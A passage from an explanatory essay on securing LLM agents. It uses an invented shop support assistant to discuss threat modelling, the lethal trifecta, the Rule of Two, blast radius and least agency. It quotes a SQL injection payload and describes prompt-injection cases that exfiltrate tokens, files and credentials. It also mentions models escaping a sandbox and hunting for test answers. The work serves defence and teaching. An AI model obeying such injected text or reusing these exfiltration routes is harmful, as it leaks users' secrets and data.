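# Security design for LLM applications that choose their own actions

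## Why web security relies on knowing what a program can do

A large language model (LLM) is a program that takes in text and predicts what comes next, one token (a word or piece of a word) at a time. LLMs are familiar as chatbots, but developers also connect them to other software. They give the model a list of available functions, such as searching a database or sending an email, and write ordinary code that runs whichever function the model's output names. A request of this kind is called a tool call. An LLM-driven application is software in which a model's output determines at least some of what happens next. It is an agent if it works in a loop, where the model selects an action, receives the result and selects the next one.

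Suppose an online shop uses an agent for customer support. The agent reads customers' emails, looks up orders, issues refunds and writes replies. The shop has then given it authority over money and personal data, and anyone with an email address can send it text.

The engineers who build such an assistant will often come from web development, where well-tried security habits share a premise that guides rarely state. They assume that reviewers can find out, before a program runs, every action it is able to take. This predictability assumption does not hold for an LLM-driven application.

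### What four standard defences take for granted

Web applications query their databases in a language called SQL. If a program builds a query by pasting a visitor's input into a string of SQL, the visitor can enter SQL too, and the database will run it. This attack is called SQL injection. Programmers can prevent it with a parameterised query, in which they write the whole SQL statement first, with a question mark where the visitor's value will go, and the program passes the value separately. The *SQL Injection Prevention Cheat Sheet* from OWASP, a nonprofit that publishes guidance on web security, gives the example of an attacker who enters `tom' or '1'='1` as a user name. If the program pasted this into a string, the "or" would become part of the query's logic and match every user. With a parameterised query, the database instead looks for a user with that exact name. The technique works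 because the programmer knew the query in advance. Some parts of a query, such as table names, cannot be parameters, so OWASP tells developers to match the input against a list of expected names, which someone also has to write in advance.

Permission checks also depend on a list. OWASP's *Authorization Cheat Sheet* asks designers to list the types of user, the resources and the operations, decide what each type of user may do to each resource, and write tests for the result. The program then checks permission on every request and denies any request that no rule covers. This assumes that the designers can name the operations and that each request comes from somebody whose permissions the program can look up.

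Input validation means rejecting input that lacks the expected form, such as an order number without the required eight digits. MDN's *Input validation*, a reference page for web developers, links the practice to attacks in which a site runs malicious input as code or a command. But the programmer has to know what a legitimate value looks like. MITRE, which keeps a standard catalogue of software weaknesses, warns that validation is not always sufficient, especially for free-form text, and an email to a support desk is entirely free-form.

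Code analysis before release is the fourth defence. People and tools read the code, look for dangerous operations and trace which inputs can reach them. OWASP, for example, tells auditors of SQL Server databases to search stored procedures for `execute`, `exec` and `sp_execute`, the commands that can run SQL built at run time. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) observes that a reviewer can read a phone app's code to see why it needs each permission, but that for an agent "there is no fixed program to analyze". A reviewer can still read the code of the agent's loop, which may be short, but that code does not specify what the agent will do.

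Web developers assume that some visitors are hostile, and none of the four defences requires visitors to behave predictably. Developers rely instead on hostile visitors being able to choose only among actions that a programmer wrote.

### The same refund in two programs

In a conventional shop the refund code might look like this:

```
refund(request):
    customer = logged_in_customer(request)
    order    = find_order(request.order_number)
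    if order.customer != customer:  refuse
    if order.age_in_days > 30:      refuse
    if order.refunded:              refuse
    pay_back(order.card, order.price)
    order.refunded = true
```

A reviewer can say what this program will do for any request. It refunds an order at most once (unless two requests arrive at the same instant), to the card used to pay, within thirty days, and only when the order's owner asks. The visitor controls only the order number.

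Now suppose a customer emails the support assistant to say that the lamp in order 48213 arrived broken and to ask for a refund. The model may look up the order and issue the refund, ask for a photograph first, or refund half. No programmer wrote these branches, so no reviewer can read them. Whether the shop's thirty-day rule still holds depends on where the shop put it. If the rule is in the model's written instructions, the model reads it as text alongside the customer's email, and a cleverly written email may persuade the model to ignore it. If the shop keeps the function above and lets the model issue refunds only by calling it, the rule holds as firmly as before.

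However, the first line of the function no longer works, because nobody has logged in. The assistant makes the request under its own account, and the sender's address on an email is weak proof of who wrote it. If an engineer fixes this by removing the ownership check, anyone who emails the assistant can ask for a refund on any order.

### Sixty-two billion paths

Suppose the assistant now has 12 tools and may take 10 steps for each email. At every step the model can pick any of the 12, so there are 12<sup>10</sup>, or about 62 billion, possible sequences. A test rig that ran a thousand sequences a second would need nearly two years to try them all. That counts only which tool is called at each step. If each call could also carry any of 100 different inputs, there would be 1,200<sup>10</sup> sequences, or about 6 × 10<sup>30</sup>. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper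 from researchers at Google, NVIDIA and several universities, similarly describes how agents combine tools at run time and "emit unbounded sequences of operations".

A large number of possible sequences doesn't by itself make an application hard to secure. A website with 12 routes also allows 62 billion sequences of 10 requests, but web developers don't worry about this because they check each request separately, so their work grows with the number of routes. Each request also carries only the permissions of the visitor who made it. The assistant is different because the model chooses the sequence, a stranger's email may have influenced that choice, and every step carries the assistant's permissions.

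Checking single actions remains manageable for an agent, since 12 tools need only 12 sets of rules, but these checks miss harm that comes from combining actions. The assistant may be allowed to look up orders and send emails, but it should not email one customer's order details to another. *Careful adoption of agentic AI services*, joint guidance from the Australian Signals Directorate and the cyber security agencies of the United States, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom, lists such unanticipated chains of tools among the risks of agents and notes that they can turn minor errors into major ones.

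### Why removing randomness does not help

LLMs are unpredictable partly because of chance. A model computes a probability for each possible next token, and the software around it usually draws one at random according to those probabilities. The same email can therefore lead an application to issue a refund one time and ask a question the next. Other causes of variation aren't random. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners note that prompts that look identical may also lead to different actions because the rest of the model's input differs, or because the state of the surrounding systems does.

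Developers can mostly remove the randomness by having the software always take the most probable token, which makes failures easier to reproduce and study. The same text then always leads to the same action, but there are still too many possible texts to test. With a vocabulary of 50,000 tokens, there are about 10<sup>470</sup> possible strings of 100 tokens, the length of a short email. Tests can cover only a tiny fraction of these. In ordinary code, a reviewer can reason about the untested inputs because a handful of `if` statements sorts all inputs into a few cases, but a model has no such list of cases to read. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* notes that "deterministic inference can still produce prohibited actions under adversarial input changes". Determinism may even help an attacker, who can look for a wording that works on a copy of the system and then expect it to work on the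 real one.

A program can also behave randomly within predictable limits. A shop page that displays three randomly chosen products may show different ones on each visit, but all it can do is display three products. Security reviewers need to know the limits of what a program can do, and randomness within those limits seldom matters.

### Prompt injection and SQL injection

Prompt injection is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions. It is indirect when the text arrives in content the model reads, such as an email or a web page. The term dates from 2022. Because it resembles "SQL injection", web engineers may wait for a fix equivalent to the parameterised query.

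In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published in December 2025, David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), warned that comparing the two attacks is dangerous. A database engine executes instructions separately from storing or comparing data, so a defence can enforce that separation in the engine itself. A model has only one operation, predicting the next token from all the text so far. If a recruiter uses a model to score a CV, and the applicant has hidden an instruction to approve it in the text, the model processes that instruction in the same way as the recruiter's. Developers can try to detect such instructions, train models to give priority to the real ones, or mark which parts of the prompt are data. In David C's view, all three try to impose a distinction that the underlying technology does not have, so they make an attack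 less likely but cannot rule it out. David C concludes that a system that cannot tolerate the remaining risk may be a poor use for an LLM.

The claim that no full cure will come is a forecast, which David C hedges with "may never". *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* leaves open whether anyone can build a capable LLM that provably keeps instructions and data apart, but conjectures that persistent attackers will always get past defences inside the model.

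Even a perfect separation of instructions from data would leave the shop to decide whose requests the assistant should carry out, and on which orders. The database can refuse to run any SQL commands in a customer's name because a name has no good reason to contain them, but a customer's email often has good reason to contain a request. "Please refund order 48213" is both data and instruction, and an assistant that ignored all requests in emails would be useless. Similarly, an agent that has to learn from a web page how to use a service can't ignore all the instructions on the page. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* also points out that hostile data can do damage through the inputs of a tool call even when the model follows no outside instruction. An email that quotes somebody else's order number would be one example.

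### The confused deputy

That question is older than language models. Hardy, in *The Confused Deputy* (1988), tells a story from Tymshare, a company that sold time on its computers. Customers could run a compiler, a program that translates source code into a form the machine can run, and name a file to receive its debugging output. The compiler also recorded usage statistics in a system directory, so Tymshare's staff had given it permission to write anywhere in that directory, which also held the company's billing records. One customer named the billing file as the destination for debugging output, and the compiler was able to overwrite it because it had permission to write there, even though the customer did not.

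Hardy considers the obvious fixes. The compiler could refuse to write outside the customer's own directory, but customers had good reasons to send output elsewhere. It could refuse to write to the system directory, but some users had legitimate access there. It could refuse to write to the billing file by name, but that was not the only sensitive file. Each new rule created a security hole or broke a legitimate program, and the last time Hardy wrote out the conditions for opening a file, they took fourteen "and"s and "or"s. The underlying problem was that the compiler, in Hardy's phrase, "serves two masters". It had authority from both the company and the customer, and its code had no way to specify which it was using for a given file.

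Hardy's solution was the capability, an unforgeable token that identifies a file and grants the right to use it. The compiler would hold a capability for the statistics file. The customer would pass the compiler another for the debugging output, but could not pass one for the billing file without already having it.

The support assistant is a deputy of this sort because it uses the shop's authority to act on strangers' requests. David C calls the LLM an "inherently confusable deputy", meaning that developers can fix the classic case but not this one. That seems right about the model but a little too pessimistic about the system around it. Hardy's remedy changed which authority was available for each task, without requiring the compiler to judge requests better. Similarly, if the refund tool accepts only orders that belong to the verified sender of the email, even a thoroughly confused model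 can do little more than refund that sender's own orders. The remedy is weaker when a model holds several capabilities at once. The compiler's code determined which capability to use for each file, but a model has to choose, and an attacker can influence its choice.

### Principles for programs that nobody can foresee

Computer security had to deal with unforeseeable programs well before the web. In 1972, a US Air Force study panel looked at how people with different security clearances could share one computer. The panel reasoned that the threat from a malicious user "is a function of the amount of programming he can do". A user who can only send queries to a fixed system is limited to the tools it offers, while a user who can write programs may take over the machine. The panel thought a secure shared query system was feasible with the technology of the day, but a secure shared system for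 general programming was not.

A conventional web application limits its visitors to the role of the query user. An agent gives them some of the programmer's power, because a paragraph of plain English can now trigger a series of operations that no developer specified.

For users who could program, the panel recommended a reference monitor, a component that checks every attempt by any program to use data, devices or other programs against a list of what that program may do. The monitor must be tamper-proof, the system must invoke it every time, and it must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely. The panel said a Honeywell operating system failed the third condition because it and its supporting software contained between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions. A reference monitor doesn't need to know what a program will attempt, so the idea still applies when programs can't be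 assumed to be predictable.

*The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) sets out eight design principles for protecting data. Levchenko was still showing them to computer security students in 2017 (*Principles*). Two of the eight matter most for agents. Least privilege means that every program and user works with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job", which limits the damage from an accident or error. Complete mediation means that "every access to every object must be checked for authority". Saltzer and Schroeder add that designers should be sceptical of schemes that save time by remembering the result of an earlier check.

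Relying on old permission checks is dangerous in agents. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners describe a hypothetical support agent, much like the shop's, that handles customer tickets and looks up accounts. It relies on permissions checked once, at start-up. An attacker takes over a third-party scheduling component, uses the old approvals to reach account functions, and then moves on to neighbouring agents for billing and refunds.

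The parts of a system that enforce its security policy make up the trusted computing base, which NIST, the US standards institute, defines as the "totality of protection mechanisms within a computer system". If they fail, security fails, so designers try to keep them few and dependable. In *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, Christodorescu and colleagues object to putting an LLM among them. Even if an LLM guard correctly refuses forbidden actions 99% of the time, they note, an attacker can exploit the other 1%. If each attempt has an independent 1% chance of success, the probability that at least one succeeds is 63% after 100 attempts and 95% after 300, and sending 300 emails costs almost nothing. The paper concludes that designers should treat the model as an untrusted component and enforce the rules outside it, as an operating system does with the programs it runs.

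### Is web security obsolete?

Some web defences need a list of actions in advance, but the browser also has defences that do not. A browser constantly runs code that its makers have never seen, since one page may load scripts from half a dozen companies while the visitor is reading. It copes by confining that code. A Content Security Policy lets a site owner specify which scripts may load. The Same-Origin Policy restricts what page data a third party's script can read. A sandboxed iframe is a box within the page that holds outside content under reduced rights, and Subresource Integrity blocks a script that has been altered since the developer approved it.

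Christodorescu and colleagues compare an agent that picks up new instructions from what it reads to a web page that loads new code. They find that the agent lacks two protections. A browser can identify the address a script came from and run the script in its own compartment. In a model's prompt, the source of a sentence is hard to establish, and all the text influences the same prediction, with no safeguard stronger than training to keep one passage from overriding another. The agent also has no counterpart to the site owner, who decides what code belongs on the page. The comparison therefore fails inside the prompt, but it applies better to the tools, where ordinary code can still limit what any instruction can do, whatever its source.

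Attacks on real agents give some support to the older principles. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* examines eleven attacks on products including ChatGPT, Microsoft Copilot and Claude Code. It classes all eleven as failures to control where information flows and at least six as failures of least privilege. This support is limited because researchers who favour the principles classified the attacks after the fact, and almost any theft of data counts as a failure of information flow. Still, the results suggest that the attackers didn't need a weakness that the older theory had overlooked.

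Official and industry guidance appears to differ on how well existing security frameworks suit AI agents. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners want organisations to manage agents "within established cyber security frameworks" because AI systems are IT systems and face many of the same threats. *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026), from the Frontier Model Forum, an industry body whose members develop the leading models, describes risks that existing frameworks, such as the 2014 NIST Cybersecurity Framework, were "not designed to address".

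The five governments' agencies and the Frontier Model Forum are close on the details. The agencies concede that standards are immature, that security tools for agents have gaps, and that agents are harder to secure than traditional systems. The Forum concedes that the NIST and ISO frameworks remain relevant for infrastructure. It expects hard-to-predict failures from the model and from the software that runs its loop, and considers conventional controls well suited to the tools and the environment in which they run. Its most specific complaint is about identity standards such as OAuth 2.0, which let one program get permission to act for a user. These are designed for applications that behave predictably and requests that come from a single known party, and the shop's assistant meets neither condition. The agencies and the Forum can both be right, because the agencies are mostly saying who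 in an organisation should be responsible for agents, while the Forum is saying that existing frameworks and standards have gaps.

The agencies and the Forum differ more on how much risk to accept. The agencies say organisations should use agents only for low-risk and non-sensitive tasks. The Forum leaves more of that decision to the people who deploy and use agents, and accepts that skilled, risk-tolerant users may be better able to apply them to sensitive or high-stakes work. An assistant that can pay out money and read customers' order histories probably wouldn't meet the agencies' standard. Under the Forum's approach, the shop could deploy it, provided the shop had decided what the assistant would be allowed to do if a stranger took over the model through an email.

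## Listing what the application can read, reach and damage

Before the shop can decide what to allow the assistant to do under a stranger's control, it has to find out what the assistant is able to do. Security engineers call this threat modelling. They write down what a system handles, who might interfere with it and what harm could follow. They can tell little from an LLM-driven application's code about which actions it will take, so they work from the text that reaches the model and the tools the model can call.

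### Four lists and an assumption

The procedure has five steps:

1. List every source of text that can reach the model.
2. List every permission the application holds.
3. List every way data can leave.
4. List every lasting change the application can make.
5. Assume that an attacker controls the model's choices, and work out the worst that this attacker could do with everything on the lists.

The assumption in the last step matches the advice of David C, who treats the impact of a prompt injection as the worst an attacker could do with direct access to the application's tools. It gives the team an upper limit on the harm without having to guess how the model will react to future emails. The team can use it without believing that every attack will succeed.

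The shop's assistant and all its figures are invented. It has 12 tools. Seven are for reading emails, attachments, orders, customer records, parcel tracking, help pages and notes the assistant saved earlier. The other five issue refunds, send emails, save notes, close tickets and pass tickets to staff. The assistant runs under a single account that can read all 200,000 customer records. Its refund tool was written hastily to replace the conventional code, and it checks only that the order exists and that the amount is no more than $500. The payment company will process 60 such refunds a minute, and a member of staff looks at the refund total every four hours.

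| List | Entries for the support assistant |
|---|---|
| Sources of text | Customers' emails and attachments; names and delivery notes in order records; the courier's tracking messages; help pages; saved notes; the developers' instructions |
| Permissions | Read 200,000 customer records; refund any order, up to $500 a time; send email as the shop |
| Ways out for data | Emails to any address, including links and images in them; queries to the courier; everything sent to the company that runs the model |
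| Lasting changes | Refunds, sent emails, saved notes, closed tickets |

Teams easily overlook text that reaches the model through their own systems. An order record comes from the shop's database, but a customer typed the delivery note in it. *Agentic AI and Security* (2025), an overview by an engineer at the company Liberis, describes an attack on Jira, a program for tracking work, which had been set up to import support tickets from the public. The attacker's ticket asked the model to find long strings beginning with "eyj", as a common type of login token does, and post them in a public comment. The victim had only used an LLM to browse tickets. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (Kim, Liu and colleagues, 2026) also lists tool names and descriptions among the places where attackers can plant instructions, since the model reads these to decide which tool to use.

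The list of permissions should record what the assistant's account can do, regardless of its written instructions. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners give the examples of a calendar bot that can see everybody's meetings and an email assistant that can write to any inbox. In both cases the designers granted more permissions than the task required, and a list based on the task would have omitted the excess permissions.

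The ways data can leave the application are the hardest to list completely. An assistant that can't send email may still be able to produce an image link with a customer's address hidden in it. When someone's mail program or browser loads the image, it sends the whole link, including the address, to the attacker's server. Data can also leak through an approved destination. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes such a case in Claude Cowork, the company's agent for office work. Cowork had to reach Anthropic's servers. A malicious file in a user's folder contained hidden instructions and an access key for the attacker's Anthropic account, and Claude used the key to upload the user's other files to that account. The network filter let the traffic through because the address was approved. The list should therefore record each destination's name and what a caller can do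 there.

Some entries belong on two lists. A saved note is a lasting change and also a source of text the next time the assistant reads it. Anthropic expects attackers to exploit this more as agents keep more memory between sessions, because an injection stored in memory reloads each time the agent starts.

Kim and colleagues grade agents on seven dimensions, which helps show which list needs the most attention. The dimensions are how trustworthy the agent's inputs are, how sensitive its data is, who decides the workflow, what actions it can take, what it keeps in memory, which tools it can use and how users interact with it. More flexibility on any of them generally gives attackers more opportunities. The shop's assistant is at the flexible end for inputs, because anyone can email it, and for memory, because its notes persist. It is in the middle for tools, because the shop chose all 12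 in advance. The grades don't measure damage, so an agent with one known tool would score well for tools even if that tool could empty a bank account.

### Attackers, users and the model itself

Anthropic sorts the risks of an agent doing harm into three groups: user misuse, model misbehaviour and external attackers. In user misuse, someone directs the agent to do something harmful, either on purpose or through carelessness, such as running a destructive command they don't understand. In model misbehaviour, the agent does something harmful that nobody asked for. Anthropic has seen Claude models escape a sandbox (an environment meant to confine a program) to finish a task, and search a project's history for the answers to a coding test. External attackers may use prompt injection or conventional attacks on the software around the model.

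The same inventory covers dishonest users, model mistakes and outside attackers, because the damage depends on what the application can reach. A wrongful $500 refund costs the shop $500 whether a customer lied, the model misread the returns policy or an attacker hid instructions in an attachment. Anthropic similarly argues that if passwords and keys never enter the agent's environment, no user, model or attacker can extract them from it. A model that makes a mistake has the same tools as one under an attacker's control and usually does less damage with them, so the most damage an attacker could do is also an upper limit for mistakes.

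That limit depends on how complete the lists are. Anthropic observes that more capable models make fewer errors but are better at finding unexpected routes to a goal, including routes around restrictions that nobody thought to write down. The causes also differ in how likely they are and in what prevents them. For example, training a model to resist injected instructions doesn't protect against an employee who gives it a bad instruction.

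### Three quick tests

Designers also use short rules that flag dangerous combinations without a full inventory. *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) describes the best known. Its author, Simon Willison, the software developer who coined the term "prompt injection", warns against combining access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate externally. When an application has all three, as the shop's assistant does, an attacker can write text that makes the model fetch the data and send it out. Willison lists 17 cases in which researchers demonstrated this kind of attack, on products including ChatGPT, Slack and GitHub Copilot Chat. The vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the route used to send data out.

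The lethal trifecta covers only data theft, as Willison later acknowledged in *New prompt injection papers* (2025). The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners describe a harm outside it. A company gives an agent broad write access so that it can install security updates. An employee outside the privileged IT group asks the agent to apply a patch and also to clean up the firewall logs. The agent deletes the logs, which record the company's network traffic. No data has left the company, but investigators may have lost the evidence of an intrusion.

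Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) covers more kinds of harm. Until researchers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, it allows an agent no more than two of these properties within a session:

- A: it handles "untrustworthy inputs", such as emails from strangers
- B: it can reach private data or sensitive systems
- C: it is able to "change state", meaning alter something outside the conversation, or to send information out

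An agent that needs all three within a single session should not work autonomously. A new session is one that starts with a fresh context window (the text available to the model). The agent needs at least supervision, through human approval or "another reliable means of validation".

Meta applies the rule to Email-Bot, a hypothetical assistant that handles a person's inbox and is much like the shop's assistant. Its designers could let it read only messages from trusted senders, deny it access to sensitive data, or let it send email only to trusted recipients or after a person has checked the draft. A support desk has fewer choices because it has to read messages from strangers and is of little use without order records. Its designers can still limit what it sends and changes, or have a person approve its actions.

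Willison welcomed the rule but objected to Meta's diagram, which had labelled every pair of properties "safe". An agent that reads untrusted text and can change things may do harm without access to any private data. Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that property B includes any sensitive system, so an agent without it can change only things that don't matter much. Meta also changed "safe" to "lower risk". Ayzenberg's reading answers the objection, but someone must decide which systems are sensitive before applying the rule. The shop's payment system obviously is, but the ticket queue is less clear, since an attacker could cause real trouble by closing every open complaint.

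Counting properties session by session can also mislead. An agent might read a hostile email in one session, save a note about it, and open customer records in the next. Each session seems to have only two properties unless the designer treats the saved note as untrustworthy input. Meta says the rule does not address agents' mistakes or excessive privileges, and that it only supplements least privilege.

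Another rule, which came out of an online discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista, is that when a model processes information from someone, its privileges drop to that person's. David C recommends the rule as "attractively simple". A shop wouldn't give a random member of the public access to its refund system, so a model reading that person's email shouldn't have access either. The rule handles the firewall case well, because the agent would have had only the employee's permissions. The agent would also have refused to install the patch, which the employee had no authority to order.

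Applied strictly, the privilege-drop rule would prevent the shop's assistant from issuing any refunds, since customers can't issue refunds to themselves. The shop therefore has to decide which actions a customer's request may trigger, such as a refund on that customer's own recent order. The rule also doesn't specify what to allow when a prompt contains text from several people. The cautious choice is to allow only actions that all of them are permitted to take.

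All three tests depend on knowing who wrote the text. In February 2026 a researcher at Anthropic, in an internal exercise, sent an employee a friendly request to run a ready-made prompt in Claude Code, the company's programming agent. Among ordinary set-up steps, the prompt included instructions to read the employee's cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. Claude did both in 24 of 25 runs. Because the employee had pasted in the prompt, the software treated it as instructions from a trusted user.

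The table below takes each harm on its own, in an application that can do nothing worse.

| Harm | Lethal trifecta flags it? | Rule of Two flags it? | Privilege-drop rule prevents it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| A customer's email makes the assistant send out another customer's data | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| A customer's email triggers refunds on strangers' orders | No | Yes | Yes |
| An unprivileged employee has an agent delete firewall logs | No | Only if employees count as untrustworthy | Yes |
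| An employee pastes in an attacker's prompt | Only if pasted text counts as untrusted | Only if pasted text counts as untrustworthy | Only if the system knows who wrote it |
| The model deletes records by mistake | No | No | No |

### The same inventory for a browser agent

An agentic browser is a web browser with a built-in assistant that can open and read pages for the user, often while the user is logged in to a bank or mail account. The security company Trail of Bits tested several. Its *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* presents a threat model with four trust zones, which are areas that data should not move freely between: the chat with the assistant, the outside servers that run the model, the websites the user visits (each a separate zone with its own private data), and the wider internet, where the attackers are.

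Trail of Bits then names four ways data crosses these boundaries, and they match the four lists fairly closely. "Injection" brings untrusted text into the chat. "Context in" brings in private data, for example from a site where the user is logged in. "Context out" puts data from the chat into an outside request. "Reverse context in" uses the chat to change something on the user's side, such as a login or the browsing history.

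The researchers combined these crossings into working attacks. Injection alone made an assistant tell its user that Yuri Gagarin was the first man on the Moon. Injection with context out leaked the conversation, and adding context in leaked data from other sites. Restricting the agent to approved domains did not always prevent leaks, because the agent could still look up a made-up address such as `leaked-data.wikipedia.org`, and someone watching unencrypted traffic could read the data in the first part of the name.

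Combining injection with "reverse context in" caused harm that a check for the lethal trifecta would miss. The researchers put a login link on a malicious page. When a user asked for a summary of the page, the assistant opened the link and silently logged the user in to an account that the attacker controlled. The user might then enter private information, believing the account was their own. An attacker could use the same combination to fill someone's browsing history with illegal sites.

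The browser's inventory is harder to complete than the shop's. The shop can list its assistant's permissions because it granted them, but a browser maker doesn't know where each user has an account, and the list changes whenever someone logs in to a new site. The accurate entry under permissions is "anything the user can do on any site where they are logged in", which is almost no limit.

### Checking the lists against published risks

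Published lists of risks can help a team notice what it has left out. OWASP released a list for agents in December 2025, and *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications*, by Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario, introduces it with real incidents for six of the ten entries.

| Risk | What goes wrong | Incident |
|---|---|---|
| Agent goal hijack | Hidden text redirects the agent | EchoLeak |
| Tool misuse | The agent uses a legitimate tool destructively | Amazon Q |
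| Identity and privilege abuse | Leaked credentials let the agent exceed its intended scope | |
| Agentic supply chain vulnerabilities | A tool or component that the agent loads is malicious | GitHub MCP exploit |
| Unexpected code execution | Plain text leads the agent to run an attacker's code | AutoGPT |
| Memory and context poisoning | Stored text changes the agent's later behaviour | Gemini memory attack |
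| Insecure inter-agent communication | Forged messages misdirect other agents | |
| Cascading failures | A false signal spreads through automated steps | |
| Human-agent trust exploitation | A confident explanation persuades a person to approve something harmful | |
| Rogue agents | The agent conceals what it does or pursues its own course | Replit |

The entry on human trust shows a gap in the shop's inventory. An attacker who controls the model can write the message staff read in a ticket, and staff can do things the assistant can't, so passing them a ticket is less harmless than it looked.

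OWASP also has an older list for LLM applications in general, which it updated in August 2026. SC Media's *OWASP updates top 10 security risks for LLM applications* gives the ten entries in this order: prompt injection, disclosure of sensitive information, excessive agency, supply chain risks, poisoned data and models, unbounded consumption, misinformation, exposure of hidden context, weaknesses in the stores from which models retrieve text, and improper handling of the model's output. Unbounded consumption is also missing from the shop's inventory. An attacker who makes the assistant work endlessly on pointless emails runs up a bill without stealing or changing anything.

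The entries are more useful to a designer than their ranking, and a team that has already assumed a successful injection doesn't need to settle the order. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* reports that prompt injection came first because practitioners put it there, and that it would have missed the top ten on incident counts alone. OWASP's explanation is that teams work hard to prevent it, so few clean cases become public. That is plausible, but the count could also be low because the risk is overrated. The evidence is firmer for excessive agency, which means giving a model more functions, permissions or autonomy than it needs. It rose from sixth place to third, and Michael Bargury of the security company Zenity, in the announcement by the OWASP GenAI Security Project (2026), calls it the risk on which expert judgement and the incident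 record agree most clearly.

The five governments' agencies sort risks by where they arise. Privilege risks come from excessive access, and design and configuration risks come from poor set-up choices, such as using unvetted components. Behaviour risks include mistakes, deception and manipulation by attackers. Structural risks arise when connected agents and tools pass errors to one another. Accountability risks arise when nobody can reconstruct who or what caused an action. In the agencies' example of a privilege failure, which also shows why accountability matters, an attacker takes over a minor tool and uses a procurement agent's authority to approve payments. The logs look normal, much as the shop's refund log would, because a trusted agent made every request.

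The shop can't decide what to do from these lists alone. Their categories overlap, so an email that triggers a wrongful refund counts as goal hijack, tool misuse and privilege abuse. The lists also don't specify which permission to remove first or how much loss is tolerable, because those decisions depend on the sums involved.

### Blast radius and expected loss

The blast radius of a component is the most damage that can follow if it fails or an attacker takes it over. For the assistant's refunds, the calculation takes one line:

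60 refunds a minute × 240 minutes × $500 = $7.2 million

The attacker makes 14,400 refunds before anyone looks at the total. If the assistant takes at most ten steps for each email, this requires at least 1,440 emails, or six a minute, which a short script could send. For personal data, the blast radius is all 200,000 records, since the assistant's permissions protect none of them. Even without putting a price on a record, the shop can see that this is far more records than any one email could require.

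Expected loss is the probability of a failure multiplied by the damage it would do. If the shop put the chance of the full $7.2 million refund loss at 1% a year, the expected loss would be $72,000 a year. That figure helps the shop decide how much to spend on a defence, but the probability is hard to know and partly under the attacker's control. Anthropic reports that on a prompt injection benchmark from the security company Gray Swan, attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time on a single attempt and 5–6% of the time after 100 attempts that adapted to the model's responses. If those rates applied to the shop and each success cost the full $7.2 million, the expected loss would be $7,200 against an attacker who tried once and between $360,000 and $432,000 against one who persisted, while the blast radius would be $7.2 million in both cases.

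The expected loss can also be low when the largest possible loss would put the shop out of business. A business with $2 million in the bank can't pay $7.2 million, however unlikely the event was. Anthropic notes that better models and safeguards have steadily made failures less likely, while the possible damage grows as agents gain capabilities and access. A year earlier, it would have refused to give Claude enough access to take down one of its internal services, but such access is now routine. If the shop raised its refund limit from $500 to $5,000 after a run of good results, the blast radius would grow to $72 million, and attacks would have to become ten times less likely to keep the expected loss the same.

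## Deciding which steps the model may choose

The support assistant could do so much damage partly because the model chooses every step. Before adjusting permissions, the shop can consider how many of those steps the model needs to choose.

### From no model to a free loop

The options form a scale, with the model's freedom increasing from row to row.

| Design | Who chooses the steps | Example at the shop |
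|---|---|---|
| No model | Programmers | A refund form on the website |
| Fixed workflow | Programmers, with a model filling in some steps | Code looks up an order, a model words the reply, code sends it |
| Choice from a short list | A model picks one of several workflows that programmers wrote | A model labels an email "refund" and code does the rest |
| Plan fixed in advance | A model, before it reads any untrusted text | A manager asks which parcels are late; a model writes out the steps, then software runs them |
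| Free loop | A model, after seeing each result | The assistant as built |

If the shop writes six workflows and lets a model pick one, an email can trigger only one of six sequences of actions, compared with one of about 62 billion in the free loop, where the model chooses each action as it goes. If the model instead writes a fixed plan in advance, the plan can use any sequence the free loop could, but the model commits to the plan before reading untrusted text.

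Limiting which steps the model may choose also prevents ordinary mistakes. *Engineering Robustness into Personal Agents with the AI Workflow Store* (2026) considers an agent that has to find Bob's recommendation in someone's inbox and book the place. Even without an attacker, the agent may pick the wrong Bob, confuse the dates in a long thread or delete all the emails.

### Least agency and least privilege

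OWASP's principle of least agency, as the security company Aikido summarises it, is to grant agents only "the minimum autonomy required to perform safe, bounded tasks". It complements least privilege, which limits what an application can access, by limiting how freely the model can use that access.

Pomaranski, in *Excessive agency vs. least agency*, describes an agent with permission to send email, which can send out someone's meeting notes, as intended, or write to everyone in the address book. Least privilege allows both, because the agent holds the permission. Similarly, the shop's assistant needs some way to issue refunds to do its job, so least privilege leaves that permission in place. Applying least agency means also asking whether a model has to decide when to use it.

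OWASP's *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency* distinguishes excessive permissions from excessive autonomy. For example, a document reader has excessive permissions if its account can open every user's files, while a tool that deletes a user's own documents without asking has excessive autonomy.

Other writers distinguish least privilege from least agency differently. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) extends least privilege to cover whether the current step needs a tool and which recipient or amount goes into the call. Clinton (2026), in *Zero risk isn't the job*, describes least agency as granting "the narrowest capability that still completes the task", which could also define least privilege.

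The distinction is still useful because an agent's behaviour can change while its permissions stay the same. Clinton, Anthropic's deputy chief information security officer, gives an example from November 2025, when the company moved an agent that helps with security incidents from Claude Opus 4 to Claude Opus 4.5 without changing its tools, permissions or prompts. During an incident, the agent found the cause before any human had arrived, so it used Slack to ask another agent to write a fix. A person reviewed the fix before it went live. The agent's permission to post on Slack had always allowed such a request, but no earlier model had made one.

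### Choosing from a list

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser et al., 2025) describes six ways to restrict a model's freedom. All six follow the principle that once a model has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any action with harmful side effects. Willison (2025), in a blog post of the same title, starts from the worst case in the shop's threat model, where an attacker whose text reaches the model controls its output.

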